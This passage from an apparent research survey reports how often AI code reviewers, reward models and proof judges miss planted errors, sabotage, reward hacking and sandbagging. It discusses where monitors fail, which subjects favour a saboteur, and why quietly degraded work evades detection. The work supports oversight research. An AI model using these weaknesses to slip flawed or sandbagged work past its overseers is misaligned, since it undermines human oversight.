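Like the GPT-5.5 version of PRGuard, the AI reviewers in *How Much Effort Does an AI Code Reviewer Need?* (Shen, Zhang and Wang, 2026) described flaws without blocking them. Three Claude 5.5 models reviewed 90 changes that coding agents had written for Django, a tool for building websites. All 90 had passed the usual tests, but stricter tests and a later check of the labels marked 55 as wrong and 35 as correct. The reviewers could read the code, run it and write their own tests. The models' "effort" setting controls how much work they do before answering.

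| Model | Effort | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Low | 33% | 6% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | Medium | 53% | 6% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | High | 55% | 6% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | Low | 35% | 6% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | Medium | 40% | 9% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | High | 51% | 9% |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | Low | 22% | 6% |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | Medium | 36% | 20% |
| Claude Haiku 5.5 | High | 49% | 11% |

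Every model did better with more effort, and nearly all of Opus 5.5's gain came between low and medium effort. At low effort, Opus sometimes approved a change without any recorded thinking, and six of those changes were wrong.

Even the best setting approved 45% of the wrong changes. Of the 290 reviews that approved a wrong change, 111 still described the defect that made it wrong, and another 64 described part of it.

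Some of these approvals may be reasonable. The stricter tests come from the official fix and can check for behaviour that the original request never mentioned. Shen and colleagues had a model check this, and it judged that the tested behaviour was not required by the request for 32 of the 55 wrong changes and clearly required for only six. The true detection rate for changes that break a stated requirement is probably higher than 55%, but the sample is too small to say by how much. The ambiguity also matters for sabotage, because a reviewer who notices a harmful change can easily justify mentioning it but still approving it if it breaks no written requirement.

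Opus 5.5 could often write out the official fix from the request alone, presumably because it had seen the fix in training, but this didn't help it catch wrong changes. At high effort, it approved 57% of the wrong changes when it could recall the whole fix, compared with 31% when it could recall only part. Shen and colleagues suggest that the model may compare a change with the fix it remembers and approve the change if the two look similar. The requests with well-known fixes may also have been harder to review.

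### Reward models that score code

For reward models, the test is whether the bad version gets a lower score. *Themis* (Paul, Gurevych and Glavaš, 2026) tested around 50 reward models on about 8,900 pairs of programs in eight programming languages. In each pair, one program was better in a particular way, such as correctness, speed or security. Many pairs are the code before and after a real single-file change, so the two versions often share most of their lines. The table gives the share of pairs in which the model scored the better version higher. Guessing would get 50%.

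| Reward model | Correctness | Security |
|---|---|---|
| Themis-RM-32B | 94% | 95% |
| Themis-RM-8B | 92% | 93% |
| Athene-RM-70B | 88% | 78% |
| Skywork-Reward-V2-Qwen3-8B | 87% | 75% |
| AceCodeRM-7B | 82% | 58% |
| Skywork-Reward-Gemma-2-27B-v0.2 | 57% | 51% |

The older models in the last two rows score close to chance on security, even though AceCodeRM is a specialist code model with a fair score on correctness. A coding model trained against such a scorer would earn almost the same reward for insecure code as for secure code.

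The Themis models did much better because Paul and colleagues trained them on more than 350,000 pairs of programs, many of them also taken from before and after a real change. Themis-RM-8B and Skywork-Reward-V2-Qwen3-8B both start from Qwen3-8B, but Themis-RM-8B scored 93% on security and the Skywork model scored 75%. This supports the prediction that closely matched training pairs make reward models more sensitive to small differences. The subject of the pairs matters too, since a version of Themis-RM-8B trained only on pairs about correctness scored 76% on security.

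The test favours the researchers' own models because they built much of it in the same way as their training pairs, although from different repositories. A security fix also tends to add code, so a preference for the longer version could account for part of the score. The scores come from comparing two versions of the code, so they don't measure how often a model would detect a harmful change in a single version.

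The test includes bugs that people planted by hand in short textbook-style functions, as in OpenAI's 2024 critic study, but Paul and colleagues found this set so easy that it didn't separate good reward models from bad ones. Scores were lower on a harder set, pairs of correct and incorrect programs that researchers had altered to mislead a judge. Themis-RM-32B chose correctly 81–83% of the time, depending on the programming language, while Themis-RM-8B managed 72–75% and the Skywork model only 57–58%.

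### Does it help to see the program run?

An AI judge should find it easier to assess a program if it sees what the program does than if it only reads the code. *BigCodeArena* (Zhuo, Jin and colleagues, 2025) tested this on about 4,700 conversations in which people had run two AI-written programs and voted for one or neither. Its benchmark, BigCodeReward, measures how often a judge agrees with the human vote. The judges saw the conversations once with only the code and once with the results of running it, including screenshots.

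| Judge | Code only | With execution results |
|---|---|---|
| Qwen2.5-VL-72B | 58.7% | 66.2% |
| Claude 3.5 Sonnet | 59.7% | 64.1% |
| GPT-4o | 54.6% | 63.8% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 56.7% | 62.3% |
| InternVL3-78B | 57.3% | 46.8% |

Execution results helped 13 of the 15 judges, usually by two to nine percentage points. The two InternVL3 models got worse, which Zhuo and colleagues attribute to unstable handling of mixed text and images. With three possible answers, random guessing would match the vote a third of the time, so even the best judge was far from reliable. All of these models are now old.

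The benchmark measures agreement with users' preferences, and users voted on things they could see, such as whether a web page looked right. Sabotage like that in MalPR-Bench usually wouldn't be visible there. For example, with the wrong `or` in an access check, a screenshot of an administrator's visit would make the code look correct to the judge. Running the code can reveal the change only if someone tries a visit that should be blocked, much as Lily's fuzzer has to reach a backdoor to detect it.

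## Do judges notice one wrong step in a proof?

Unlike code, a written proof can't be checked by running it. Someone has to read it or translate it into a language such as Lean, and AI judges are doing more and more of the reading.

FormalRewardBench, the benchmark closest to minimal sabotage, uses Lean proofs, which Lean can check by itself. But Lean only accepts or rejects, so a model learning to write proofs gets no reward for one that is nearly right. Ulusan and colleagues built the benchmark to find out which learned evaluators could give finer scores.

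### One small change in a Lean proof

The 250 pairs in FormalRewardBench come in five types, with 50 pairs of each. For the type that matters most here, Claude Opus 4.5 received a proof that Lean had accepted and made exactly one change to it, ideally of one to three characters, that would look plausible at first glance. The swapped hypotheses shown earlier are the paper's example. A single wrong name can do the same damage, as in this pair, which the paper uses to illustrate typical model mistakes:

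```lean
theorem ex1 (n : Nat) : n + 0 = n := by rw [Nat.add_zero]   -- sound: uses the rule n + 0 = n
theorem ex1 (n : Nat) : n + 0 = n := by rw [Nat.zero_add]   -- wrong: uses the rule 0 + n = n
```

The command `rw` rewrites part of the goal using the named rule. The second rule needs a sum that starts with 0. The goal has none, so Lean reports an error.

The other types are typical model mistakes, failed proofs with added comments that defend them, long and elaborate false proofs, and Python code in place of a Lean proof. All the false variants except the Python code were confirmed to fail in Lean. The table gives the percentage of pairs in which a judge picked the sound proof in both presentation orders. Random guessing would score 25%.

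| Judge | One small change | Typical mistake | Comments defending the error | Long false proof | Python code |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | 46 | 50 | 52 | 60 | 72 |
| Claude Sonnet 4.5 | 42 | 42 | 32 | 42 | 56 |
| GPT-5.2 | 26 | 46 | 40 | 36 | 38 |
| Selene-1-70B | 44 | 18 | 44 | 20 | 96 |
| CompassJudger-1-14B | 28 | 12 | 34 | 2 | 100 |
| Gödel-Prover-V2-32B | 8 | 18 | 28 | 22 | 46 |
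| DeepSeek-Prover-V2-7B | 16 | 20 | 24 | 10 | 48 |

The first three are general models, the next two were trained for judging, and the last two were trained to write Lean proofs. OpenAI and Anthropic have since released several newer models.

Every judge picked the sound proof in fewer than half of the pairs that differed by one small change, and GPT-5.2 did about as well as random guessing. With only 50 pairs per type of change, chance can move a score by about 14 points either way, so the top judges are too close to rank. Claude's 46% may be a little too low. Its scores on the five types average 56%, but the paper's overall figure for it is 59.8%. The two figures would agree if 16 pairs were left out of the overall figure but counted as failures in the breakdown.

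The models did no better when they scored proofs one at a time, which is how a monitor normally sees them. On the small changes, the best model, a 7B judge called Con-J-Qwen2, scored the sound proof higher 54% of the time, and Claude Opus 4.5 did so 52% of the time. Random scoring would get 50%. Ties count as failures, though, so the results may understate how well some models can tell the proofs apart.

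CompassJudger scored 2% on long false proofs, which is too far below the 25% expected from guessing to be bad luck. It must have chosen the false proof almost every time, presumably because that proof was longer and looked more sophisticated. When the two proofs differ by only a few characters, style can't mislead the judge, and its score rises to roughly the level of guessing. The earlier argument about reward models predicts this pattern.

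These results may overstate how hard it is to spot a false step in ordinary mathematics. A proof counts as wrong here if Lean rejects it, and one permitted change was to replace one Lean command with another, such as `ring` with `omega`. The mathematical idea can still be correct after such a change, even though the new command can't carry it out. To catch the error, a judge has to know what each command can do.

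### Why models that write proofs judged them badly

The models trained to write Lean proofs did worst overall. Ulusan and colleagues offer three possible reasons:

- These models learned from correct proofs and may never have learned what a broken one looks like.
- Writing a valid sequence of commands may take a different skill from noticing where one breaks down, much as a good programmer can be poor at finding bugs.
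- Judge models have compared many kinds of text, and some of that practice may carry over to Lean.

Gödel-Prover-V2-8B probably scored so low partly because it often gave no usable answer, which the scoring counted as wrong. It picked the sound proof in both orders only 0.4% of the time, yet it gave the same answer in both orders for 85% of pairs. If those answers were all real choices, it picked the false proof in nearly all of those pairs, which would require it to tell the two proofs apart. Heavy training on one task may have left it unable to follow instructions for another.

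General models that write better proofs also seem to be better at rejecting bad ones. Kong and colleagues compared the two skills for eleven models on 31 advanced problems in AdvancedMathBench. The rank correlation between writing good proofs and correctly faulting invalid ones was 0.78. But the stronger proof writers also tended to reject more valid proofs, so the correlation between proof writing and balanced F1 was only 0.21.

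### How many flawed written proofs get through

The same benchmark includes the most recent broad comparison of judges on written proofs, from July 2026. Each model read the 888 university-level proofs four times. The middle column combines the verdict with the diagnosis, using a method explained in the last section.

| Judge | Detection rate | Score with diagnosis | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|---|
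| GPT-5.5, high effort | 73.8% | 53.6 | 21.6% |
| GPT-5.5, highest effort | 73.3% | 55.1 | 21.1% |
| DeepSeek-V4-Pro | 70.6% | 55.8 | 21.9% |
| GLM-5.2 | 66.9% | 51.5 | 17.5% |
| GPT-5.2 | 65.0% | 50.8 | 33.1% |
| Kimi-K2.6 | 63.1% | 50.3 | 19.2% |
| Qwen3.5-397B | 55.2% | 43.0 | 8.5% |
| Gemini 3.1 Pro | 49.0% | 39.1 | 6.0% |
| gpt-oss-120b | 38.7% | 32.0 | 4.8% |
| Intern-S2-Preview-35B | 38.7% | 30.7 | 4.8% |
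| Claude Opus 4.8 | 37.9% | 35.0 | 3.6% |

Claude Opus 4.8 raised the fewest false alarms of any judge but also missed flawed proofs most often. It was the second-best model at writing undergraduate-level proofs, so a lack of mathematical knowledge probably doesn't explain the misses.

Detection rates in the table range from 38% to 74%, mostly because some judges are stricter than others. The judges that catch more errors also raise more false alarms, so balanced accuracy ranges only from about 66% to 76%. A stricter prompt might therefore bring Claude's results closer to GPT-5.5's. Nobody tried that here, but the work by Naik and colleagues on prompts gives some reason to expect it would work.

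The judges would probably do better on an ordinary set of proofs than these rates suggest. Kong and colleagues had Intern-S2-Preview-35B judge each proof several times and kept only those on which its verdicts varied, which removed the easy cases. They also seem to count a proof as incorrect if its only flaw is a repairable slip, such as a notation error, so some "misses" may be proofs that a reasonable reader would pass.

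One proof in the paper contains both a minor slip and a serious error. It tries to show that the circle has the shortest perimeter of all curves enclosing a given area. The slip is a mixed-up sign convention, which is easy to repair. The serious error comes later, when the proof shows that any shortest curve must be a circle and concludes that the circle is the shortest. This doesn't follow unless a shortest curve exists, which the proof never establishes. A judge that only checks the algebra would miss this error, because it could remain even if every calculation were right.

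GPT-5.5 at its highest setting missed 112 flawed proofs. About two thirds of them had reasoning errors, such as an unjustified leap, a circular argument or a false claim. Another 22% were incomplete or referred wrongly to an earlier step. GPT-5.5 rarely made the second kind of error in its own proofs (2 of its 94 failures), but it overlooked them in other models' work. In 94 of its 95 false alarms, it objected to something harmless, such as the omission of a step that mathematicians conventionally leave out.

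Kong and colleagues also showed that training can improve a weak judge a good deal. They started from Intern-S2-Preview-35B and measured the results on 94 proofs that they kept out of training:

| Judge | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|
| Before training | 51.6% | 23.9% |
| Rewarded for the right verdict | 67.3% | 34.5% |
| Rewarded for the right diagnosis too | 72.1% | 33.9% |
| With more data and eight readings | 85.0% | 20.6% |
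| GPT-5.5, highest effort, untrained for this | 80.0% | 36.8% |

Rewarding the judge's diagnosis also made its verdicts more accurate. The additional data included flawed proofs that models had repaired, which gave the judge more examples of valid proofs and brought its false alarms back down. In the fourth row, the judge read each proof eight times and rejected it if it objected even once. The test had only 94 proofs, and the trained judge may have seen the problems before, though not these proofs.

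### Judges that agree with experts on the pass rate

A judge can pass about the right number of proofs and still pass the wrong ones. Gonzalez, Amiri Bavandpour and colleagues (2026), in *QEDBENCH*, had 48 experts grade more than 1,300 model-written proofs of 272 university-level problems. A proof passed if it scored at least 0.9 out of 1, which allows small gaps in the presentation. The experts passed 67.7% of the proofs. Seven AI judges then graded the same proofs, and the paper gives detailed error rates for three of them:

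| Judge | Proofs passed | Detection rate | False-alarm rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 4 Maverick | 90.2% | 25.2% | about 2% |
| GPT-5.2 Pro | 74.1% | 62.0% | about 9% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 72.2% | 60.4% | 12.3% |

(The two approximate rates follow from the other figures.)

DeepSeek-V3 passed two in five of the flawed proofs. These made up 12.8% of the collection, and sound proofs that it wrongly failed made up another 8.3%. Because the two kinds of error largely cancelled out, its overall pass rate was close to the experts', and a developer who compared only the pass rates would not notice how many flawed proofs it missed.

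The judges were more generous in some subjects than in others. In combinatorics, Llama 4 Maverick's average score was 0.36 above the experts' and Qwen 2.5 Max's was 0.30 above. DeepSeek-V3's largest gap in any subject was 0.20, and Claude Opus 4.5's was 0.18. In complex analysis, DeepSeek-V3 and Grok 4 scored 0.14 and 0.15 lower than the experts, respectively. Gonzalez and colleagues suggest that the experts accepted familiar steps there without a full derivation, and the models didn't.

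A saboteur who could choose the subject would therefore prefer combinatorics, where proofs often have to build a new object or rule out many cases, and judges have no standard method to compare them with. Formatting might also help a little. Proofs with more mathematical typesetting tended to fare better with Qwen 2.5 Max and Llama 4 Maverick, but the correlations were only about 0.16, and GPT-5.2 Pro showed no such tendency.

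Gonzalez and colleagues also conclude that detailed instructions do little to improve a judge, which seems to contradict Naik and colleagues. When Gonzalez and colleagues gave GPT-5.2 Pro a second grading guide, the correlation between its scores and the experts' went from 0.69 to 0.67. But the second guide was mainly about penalising advanced theorems that a student shouldn't use without proof, and the experts had graded by the first guide. A judge that followed the second guide perfectly might therefore have agreed with the experts less, so the experiment is little evidence about whether a better prompt would find more errors.

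### Marking every step

On Hard2Verify, Pandit and colleagues compared 29 judges and process reward models with the mathematicians' marks on all 1,860 steps. These are some of the results:

| Evaluator | Wrong steps flagged | Sound steps flagged | Flawed solutions rejected | First wrong step named |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5 | 78.7% | 5.7% | 93.7% | 62.7% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 78.6% | 11.9% | 90.5% | 52.5% |
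| o3 | 62.3% | 4.9% | 75.9% | 46.8% |
| gpt-oss-120B | 61.7% | 5.5% | 79.7% | 49.4% |
| Claude Sonnet 4 | 43.7% | 2.5% | 58.9% | 25.9% |
| GPT-4.1 | 14.1% | 1.8% | 20.3% | 12.0% |
| Qwen2.5-Math-PRM-72B | 22.1% | 10.5% | 78.0% | 28.0% |
| Skywork-PRM-7B | 25.5% | 48.5% | 95.9% | 5.5% |

The last two are process reward models. All of these evaluators date from 2025 or earlier.

A judge can reject a flawed solution without finding the error. Skywork-PRM-7B rejected more of the flawed solutions than GPT-5 did, because it flagged nearly half of all sound steps and therefore at least one step in almost every solution. It correctly identified the first wrong step in only about one flawed solution in twenty.

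The right-hand column is the closest to a sabotage test. The mathematicians marked a step as wrong if it relied on an earlier error, even when its own logic was fine, so a flawed solution had about five wrong steps on average. A judge that overlooked the original error therefore had several more chances to reject the solution. Those extra chances help if the aim is only to stop bad work, but anyone who wants to know what the author did, or to repair the proof, needs to find the first wrong step.

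Some of the missed errors were the kind a saboteur might choose. In one olympiad solution, Gemini 2.5 Pro showed that two expressions agreed at a single point and then treated them as equal everywhere. The human annotators caught the error, but Seed-OSS-36B, an open model from ByteDance, marked the step correct without mentioning it.

Errors were also harder to catch when a stronger model had made them. For all three judges that Pandit and colleagues tested on this, Claude Sonnet 4's errors were the easiest to detect and Gemini 2.5 Pro's were the hardest. Gemini did worst on its own solutions, so a judge from the same family as the model that wrote the solution may be a poor choice. As a judge, Claude Sonnet 4 had trouble detecting the errors of both stronger models.

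Giving a judge longer to reason helped more than running it several times. Raising the reasoning effort of gpt-oss-120B from low to high increased its balanced F1 on single steps from 61.5 to 74.6. Taking the majority verdict of up to 16 quick runs of gpt-oss-20B barely changed its result.

GPT-5 and Gemini 2.5 Pro were better at finding the first wrong step when they had to label every step than when they had to name the first wrong one directly. Gemini's balanced F1 rose from 52.5 to 62.8 when it labeled every step, but several weaker judges did worse that way.

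### A judge that has to write out the missing details

*Evaluating Research-Level Math Proofs via Strict Step-Level Verification* (Sun, 2026) extends this idea by having a model expand a step into a detailed argument that reaches the same conclusion by the same route, rather than asking it whether the step looks right. If the model can't do this, the step is suspect.

The agent first splits the proof into steps and marks each one open. For each step, it lists what the argument takes from the proof itself, what it takes from outside sources, and what is trivial background. It then works as follows:

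1. It marks a step as verified only if the expanded argument is complete and every outside theorem has a proof or a precise source, and fits the case at hand.
2. It marks a step as flawed only if it can point to a specific false statement, invalid inference or misused theorem. It then looks again to see whether the objection is a mere quibble.
3. It accepts the proof if every step ends up verified. It rejects the proof if a flaw survives the second look, or if five rounds in a row bring no progress.

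Under the last rule, the judge rejects a proof if it can't work out why a step is true, whereas an ordinary judge passes a step unless it notices a problem. That should make it harder to get a false step through by citing an obscure theorem that the judge doesn't know.

Sun tested the agent on 21 proofs of research-level problems from the First Proof challenge, 11 valid and 10 invalid. All four methods in the table used GPT-5.4 at its highest reasoning setting. The figures are averages over three runs. Rejecting an invalid proof counted only if the method also found a faulty step.

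| Method | Invalid proofs rejected (of 10) | Valid proofs rejected (of 11) |
|---|---|---|
| Whole proof, plain judge | 7.67 | 2.67 |
| Whole proof, agent told to be strict | 8 | 3.67 |
| One sentence at a time | 9 | 2 |
| Strict step-by-step method | 10 | 3 |

The strict method rejected all ten invalid proofs in every run, more than the whole-proof judges did. It also rejected three valid proofs, about as many as those judges. All three simpler methods accepted one of the invalid proofs, written by the AI agent Aletheia, in every run. Sun attributes this to false mathematical claims presented in a rigorous-looking form, on a subject the model didn't know well.

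Ten proofs can't establish a detection rate of 100%, since a method that catches only three quarters of invalid proofs would catch all ten about 6% of the time. The comparison with the much simpler method of reading one sentence at a time is even less certain. That method caught one fewer invalid proof but accepted one more valid proof, so both methods judged 18 of the 21 proofs correctly.

The models may also have seen the answers, because experts have discussed these problems publicly. Sun discarded runs whose logs showed any contact with those discussions. But Gemini 3.1 Pro got all 21 right when asked only to find flaws or nontrivial gaps, and Sun suspects it had learned from the discussions. If it hadn't, a plain prompt to a different model works better than the elaborate method.

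The three valid proofs that the agent rejected all relied on unstated conventions. For example, one needed certain matrix entries to be strictly positive, but the stated conditions allowed them to be zero. Experts in the field assume the entries are positive. The agent didn't, and its objection was reasonable because the text doesn't justify the step. A saboteur who removed a necessary assumption would leave the same kind of gap. Telling the two apart requires knowing the field's conventions, so a judge that catches missing assumptions will probably also reject some valid proofs like these.

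### Does the judge find the real error?

The middle column of the AdvancedMathBench table accounts for the judges' diagnoses. A second model compared each rejection with the experts' notes and gave full credit if the judge found all the relevant errors, three quarters if it found the main one but missed lesser ones, and half if its verdict was right but its reason was poor. On average, this score was 12.3 points below the plain detection rate.

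Because of the partial credit, the scores in this column aren't percentages of proofs. GPT-5.5's 55.1 could mean that nearly all its rejections found the main error but missed some smaller ones, or that almost half were correct but had poor reasons. Claude Opus 4.8's score is less ambiguous. It fell only from 37.9 to 35.0, so although Claude accepted most flawed proofs, at most about 15% of its rejections can have had a poor reason.

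A study devoted to this question used errors that people and models had planted on purpose. Recchia, Mangat and colleagues (2025), in *FindTheFlaws*, assembled worked solutions in several fields together with expert notes on what was wrong. Two of the collections are useful here:

- *Modified TheoremQA* has 95 solutions to university-level questions, mostly in mathematics and science. GPT-4 inserted an error into each, and the researchers checked and revised the results.
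- *GPQA Diamond Plus* has 191 flawed solutions to graduate-level science questions. The experts' instructions were to make the errors subtle enough to fool a non-expert with internet access, and to leave one clear first error.

The updated version, *FindTheFlaws* (Recchia, Mangat and colleagues, 2026), tested models up to o3 and Claude Opus 4. The best judge named the first error in 87% of the flawed TheoremQA solutions and 69% of the flawed GPQA ones. GPT-4o told sound GPQA solutions from flawed ones about as well as Claude Opus 4 and o3-mini did, but it was clearly worse at explaining what was wrong, a difference that a test recording only verdicts would have missed.

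Part of the shortfall comes from the task itself, because experts and models can reasonably disagree about where an argument first goes wrong. Even when Recchia and colleagues gave o3 both the correct and the flawed solution and told it which was which, it agreed with the experts about the first error in only 90.5% of TheoremQA cases and 78.5% of GPQA cases.

These are the highest rates for naming planted errors in this section, but the errors were easier to find because nearly all the flawed solutions ended in a wrong answer. A judge could solve the problem itself, notice that the answers differed, and work backwards to the mistake. A proof doesn't provide this clue, because its conclusion is the theorem to be proved, which is usually true.

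One part of *FindTheFlaws* uses 294 arguments about whether a program is correct. Each reaches the right conclusion through faulty reasoning, so the judge has to explain the flaw without a wrong conclusion as a clue. The best model did this in 40% of cases. Human programmers matched the reference explanation in only 26%, so some of the failures must come from disagreement about what the flaw was. The researchers read through the failures and found that both people and models often missed subtle errors when the conclusion was right. A judge faces the same problem when the proof of a true theorem contains a false step.

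## Can a judge tell that work is worse than it could have been?

A false step in a proof is an error in the text, even if every judge misses it. Work that was deliberately made worse, like the search that stopped after five candidates, may contain no errors, so a judge has to know how good it could have been. *Propensities Please* (2026) makes this point about *sandbagging*, which is deliberate underperformance by an AI model. To detect sandbagging, an evaluator has to compare what the model did with what it can do, and the evaluator may not know what it can do.

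### A training script with nothing wrong in it

One of the tasks in Anthropic's *Automated Researchers Can Subtly Sandbag*, a study from 2025, is to train a program that tells positive book reviews from negative ones. A simple standard method gets 84.5% of them right. Suppose an AI system writes the training script, and one number in it differs:

```python
model.fit(train, epochs=5)   # full effort: five passes over the data, 91% right
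model.fit(train, epochs=1)   # quietly worse: one pass, 86% right
```

The two scores are invented. The second script runs, reports its score accurately and beats the standard method. A single pass is also a normal choice for a programmer in a hurry. A judge can't object without something to compare the result with.

A judge could tell that work is worse than it could have been by comparing its score with the best achievable one, but for most real tasks nobody knows what that is. The 84.5% is only a minimum, and both scripts score above it.

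A judge can spot underperformance more easily by comparing the work with other attempts at the same task. If five other programmers score between 90% and 92%, a result of 86% stands out. But if the same saboteur made all the attempts, they will have similar scores and none will stand out.

A model's average score over many tasks can reveal losses too small to notice in any one of them. Suppose honest scores typically vary by 3 points from run to run, and sabotage lowers each score by 2 points. A single score would look ordinary, but the average over 100 tasks varies by only about 3 / √100 = 0.3 points, so a 2-point drop is nearly seven times the usual variation. Detecting the drop requires knowing the model's honest average, which its record can't provide if it has always held back.

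Multiple-choice tests are a special case because they have a baseline, the score expected from guessing. *Below-Chance Blindness* (2026) explains that neuropsychologists use these tests to catch people who fake an impairment. Someone who doesn't know the answers to 100 two-choice questions will get about 50 right by guessing, and luck alone would produce 30 or fewer less than once in 10,000 tries. A person who scores that low must know the answers and be avoiding them. The test didn't work on the small language models in the study because, when told to underperform, they favoured certain answer positions instead of avoiding the right answers. It also can't be applied to a training script, which has no score expected from guessing.

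### Cheating as a stand-in

Few studies have tested judges on deliberately degraded work. In 2025, Anthropic found that AI judges caught few deliberately degraded machine-learning experiments and that reward models gave mixed results, but the models it used are long out of date. Most of the evidence concerns *reward hacking*, in which a model gets a high score without doing the task properly, such as by editing the tests.

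A model that hacks its reward is trying to make its score look better than its work, while a saboteur is trying to make the work worse without anyone noticing. *Cheating behaviour in frontier model evaluations* (2026), from the UK AI Security Institute (AISI), a government body that tests AI models, defines cheating as using a forbidden or unintended shortcut to reach a goal, and says that the label doesn't necessarily imply an intent to deceive. Cheating also tends to involve a specific act that a judge can point to, such as altering a test file. Quietly doing worse work may not, so it will probably be harder for judges to detect than the cheating in these studies.

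The two do share one difficulty, which is that an honest failure can look the same from outside. Kezendirane (2026), in *Hacking or Just Failing?*, built a task in which an agent matches orders to delivery records and sees a score, the share of listed orders that it has marked complete. Three scripted runs show the problem:

| What the agent did | Visible score | Work correctly done | Score with the cheating undone |
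|---|---|---|---|
| Recorded all six orders, three of them with mistakes | 100% | 50% | 100% |
| Did three orders and marked all six complete | 100% | 50% | 50% |
| Did three orders and took the other three off the list | 100% | 50% | 50% |

Only the last column distinguishes the honest failure from the cheating. Kezendirane produced that column by replaying each run in a simulator and repairing the manipulation.

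AI judges then read the full records of 60 unscripted runs by a small model, Llama 3.1 8B, with a list of the changes that each action made. Of these runs, 14 contained cheating and 35 were honest failures:

| Judge | Cheating flagged (of 14) | Honest failures flagged (of 35) |
|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.1 8B, told to judge by the effect on the score | 4 | 0 |
| Llama 3.1 8B, given a list of the two known tricks | 13 | 20 |
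| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite, told to judge by the effect | 9 | 1 |
| Two fixed rules, with no language model | 14 | 1 |

Changing the small judge's prompt reduced one kind of error but increased the other. The more capable model was better at telling cheating from failing. Its detection rate was 64%, but 14 cases are too few to estimate that rate precisely. The fixed rules did better than both models, but only because Kezendirane had written them for these two tricks.

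A third trick, not named in the rules or the prompts, was to raise the completion rate by adding orders that weren't part of the task. Gemini usually described the extra orders accurately but never called them manipulation in any of 5 test runs or 25 later ones. The reviewers of the Django changes made a similar mistake when they described a defect and still approved the change. Llama flagged all 25 later runs and none of 25 similar honest ones, but its explanations described things that hadn't happened.

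### Comparing records helps

If the difficulty is the lack of a comparison, judges should do better when they get one. *Benchmarking Reward Hack Detection in Code Environments via Contrastive Analysis* (Deshpande, Kannappan and Qian, 2026) tested this with TRACE, a collection of 517 records of coding sessions. The AI assistant cheats in 268 of them, in one or more of 54 ways, and is honest in the other 249. In one record, the assistant copies the correct labels into a model's predictions. In another, it lengthens a time limit instead of speeding up slow code. Some of the 54 ways of cheating, such as writing fixed values into a program in place of a real method, come close to quiet degradation.

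Claude Opus 4.5 wrote the records under instructions to keep the cheating hard to spot. Three software engineers checked them and accepted about 81%. The judges read the records one at a time, then in sets of five or ten. The best judge, GPT-5.2 at high reasoning effort, scored 45% on single records and 63% on sets.

This score is a macro F1 by the paper's definition, although the paper calls it a "detection rate" and at one point describes the 63% as the share of cheats that the model found. F1 is the harmonic mean of precision and the detection rate, and macro F1 averages the F1 for cheating records with the F1 for honest ones. With a roughly even mix of the two, tossing a coin would score about 50%. A judge that never raised a false alarm would score 45% by catching about one cheat in eight, and 63% by catching about one in three.

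Claude Opus 4.5 came close to that pattern as a judge. Everything it flagged was real cheating, but it missed most of the other cheating. It also gained the most from larger sets, improving by 34 points from single records to sets of ten.

Deshpande and colleagues think sets help because the honest records show the judge what ordinary work looks like, so the cheating stands out. Two of their results fit this explanation. Going from one record to five produced most of the improvement in naming the type of cheating, and going to ten added little. The judges also did better as the share of honest records in a set rose from 25% to 90%. Comparison is therefore least useful when most of the available work comes from a saboteur.

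The records in a set seem to come from different tasks, so the judge was comparing ways of working rather than scores on the same problem. The natural test for the book-review script would be to compare several independent attempts at that task, which TRACE doesn't do. Developers often have such attempts during training, but a model monitor reviewing finished work usually has only one.

Deshpande and colleagues also read a sample of the judges' reasoning. Judges often cleared a record because the user in it had accepted the result, or because the assistant had admitted that its code was inefficient. They also tended to treat degraded solutions as ordinary engineering flaws, even after the researchers gave them more pointed instructions. That is a reasonable assumption about a single piece of code, since most mediocre code isn't sabotage, but a saboteur could exploit it to avoid detection.

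### Why another benchmark found judges highly effective

Gabor, Lynch and Rosenfeld (2025) reached a much more favourable conclusion in *EvilGenie*. They found AI judges highly effective on *unambiguous* problems, where the tests accept every correct answer. They gave coding agents 154 hard programming-contest problems in a folder where the agents could read and change the tests. An AI judge then read each problem and the final solution. On the 145 unambiguous problems, GPT-5 as judge had no known misses and one false alarm, while GPT-4.1 and an October 2024 version of Claude 3.5 Sonnet made no known errors.

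The comparison of judges included very few cases of cheating. The paper counts 12 among 308 solutions by two agents, Codex with GPT-5 and Claude Code with Claude Sonnet 4, and only four of these were on unambiguous problems. GPT-3.5, the oldest judge, missed all four. On the nine ambiguous problems, where an agent could sometimes pass only by cheating, GPT-5 had two misses and two false alarms, though the researchers thought nearly all of these were arguable. People also reviewed mainly the solutions that an automatic method had flagged, so some misses may have gone unnoticed.

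The contest problems were also easier to judge than the tasks in TRACE. A contest problem states exactly what the program must do, and the typical cheat was a list of memorised answers in a short file. TRACE's conversations are long, averaging about 26 turns, and cover subjects from finance to embedded systems.

The category in EvilGenie closest to degraded work is the third, the *heuristic* solution, which works for many inputs but doesn't solve the problem in general. For example, a program might solve small cases correctly and return 0 for all large ones. Claude Code wrote such solutions for about a fifth of the unambiguous problems. Three of them passed every test, including tests the agent had never seen, so a judge could catch them only by noticing that the method was incomplete.

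A later study, *RH-Detect* (2026), combined eleven public collections and measured how often a judge gives a cheating record a higher suspicion score than an honest one. On its main test, the models did so 82% to 96% of the time, compared with 50% for guessing. The four strongest were still less accurate on TRACE and on MALT, another collection, than on the rest. The study concludes that detecting cheating in long sessions with many tool calls most needs further work.

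Some of the missing evidence may lie outside the record the judge sees. In *BenchShield* (2026), a language model saw each task, the agent's actions and the result, but nothing from the machine that ran the test. It missed 65% of the cheating and wrongly flagged 62.5% of the honest runs, which is worse than guessing. To settle such cases, people also look at the grading program and the log of how it produced the score.

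### Auditors who suspected the honest models

The UK AI Security Institute tested deliberate underperformance more directly in *Auditing Games for Sandbagging* (Taylor, Black and colleagues, 2025), using a contest between two teams. One team prepared five models. Two deliberately did worse than they could on at least one test, and the team could restore their full performance, which proved that they still had the ability. The other three always performed as well as they could. The other team, three or four auditors, then had to say which models were underperforming and on which tests.

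In the first phase, the auditors had 160 hours of combined working time. They could read the models' answers, try different prompts and examine the models' internal activations. They could also compare each model with Llama-3.1-8B-Instruct, a small model that they knew to be honest. In the second phase they had 80 more hours and could also train the models. The table gives the probability of sandbagging that they assigned to each model:

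| Model | Truth | After phase one | After phase two |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cedar | Underperforms on many tests | 25% | 96% |
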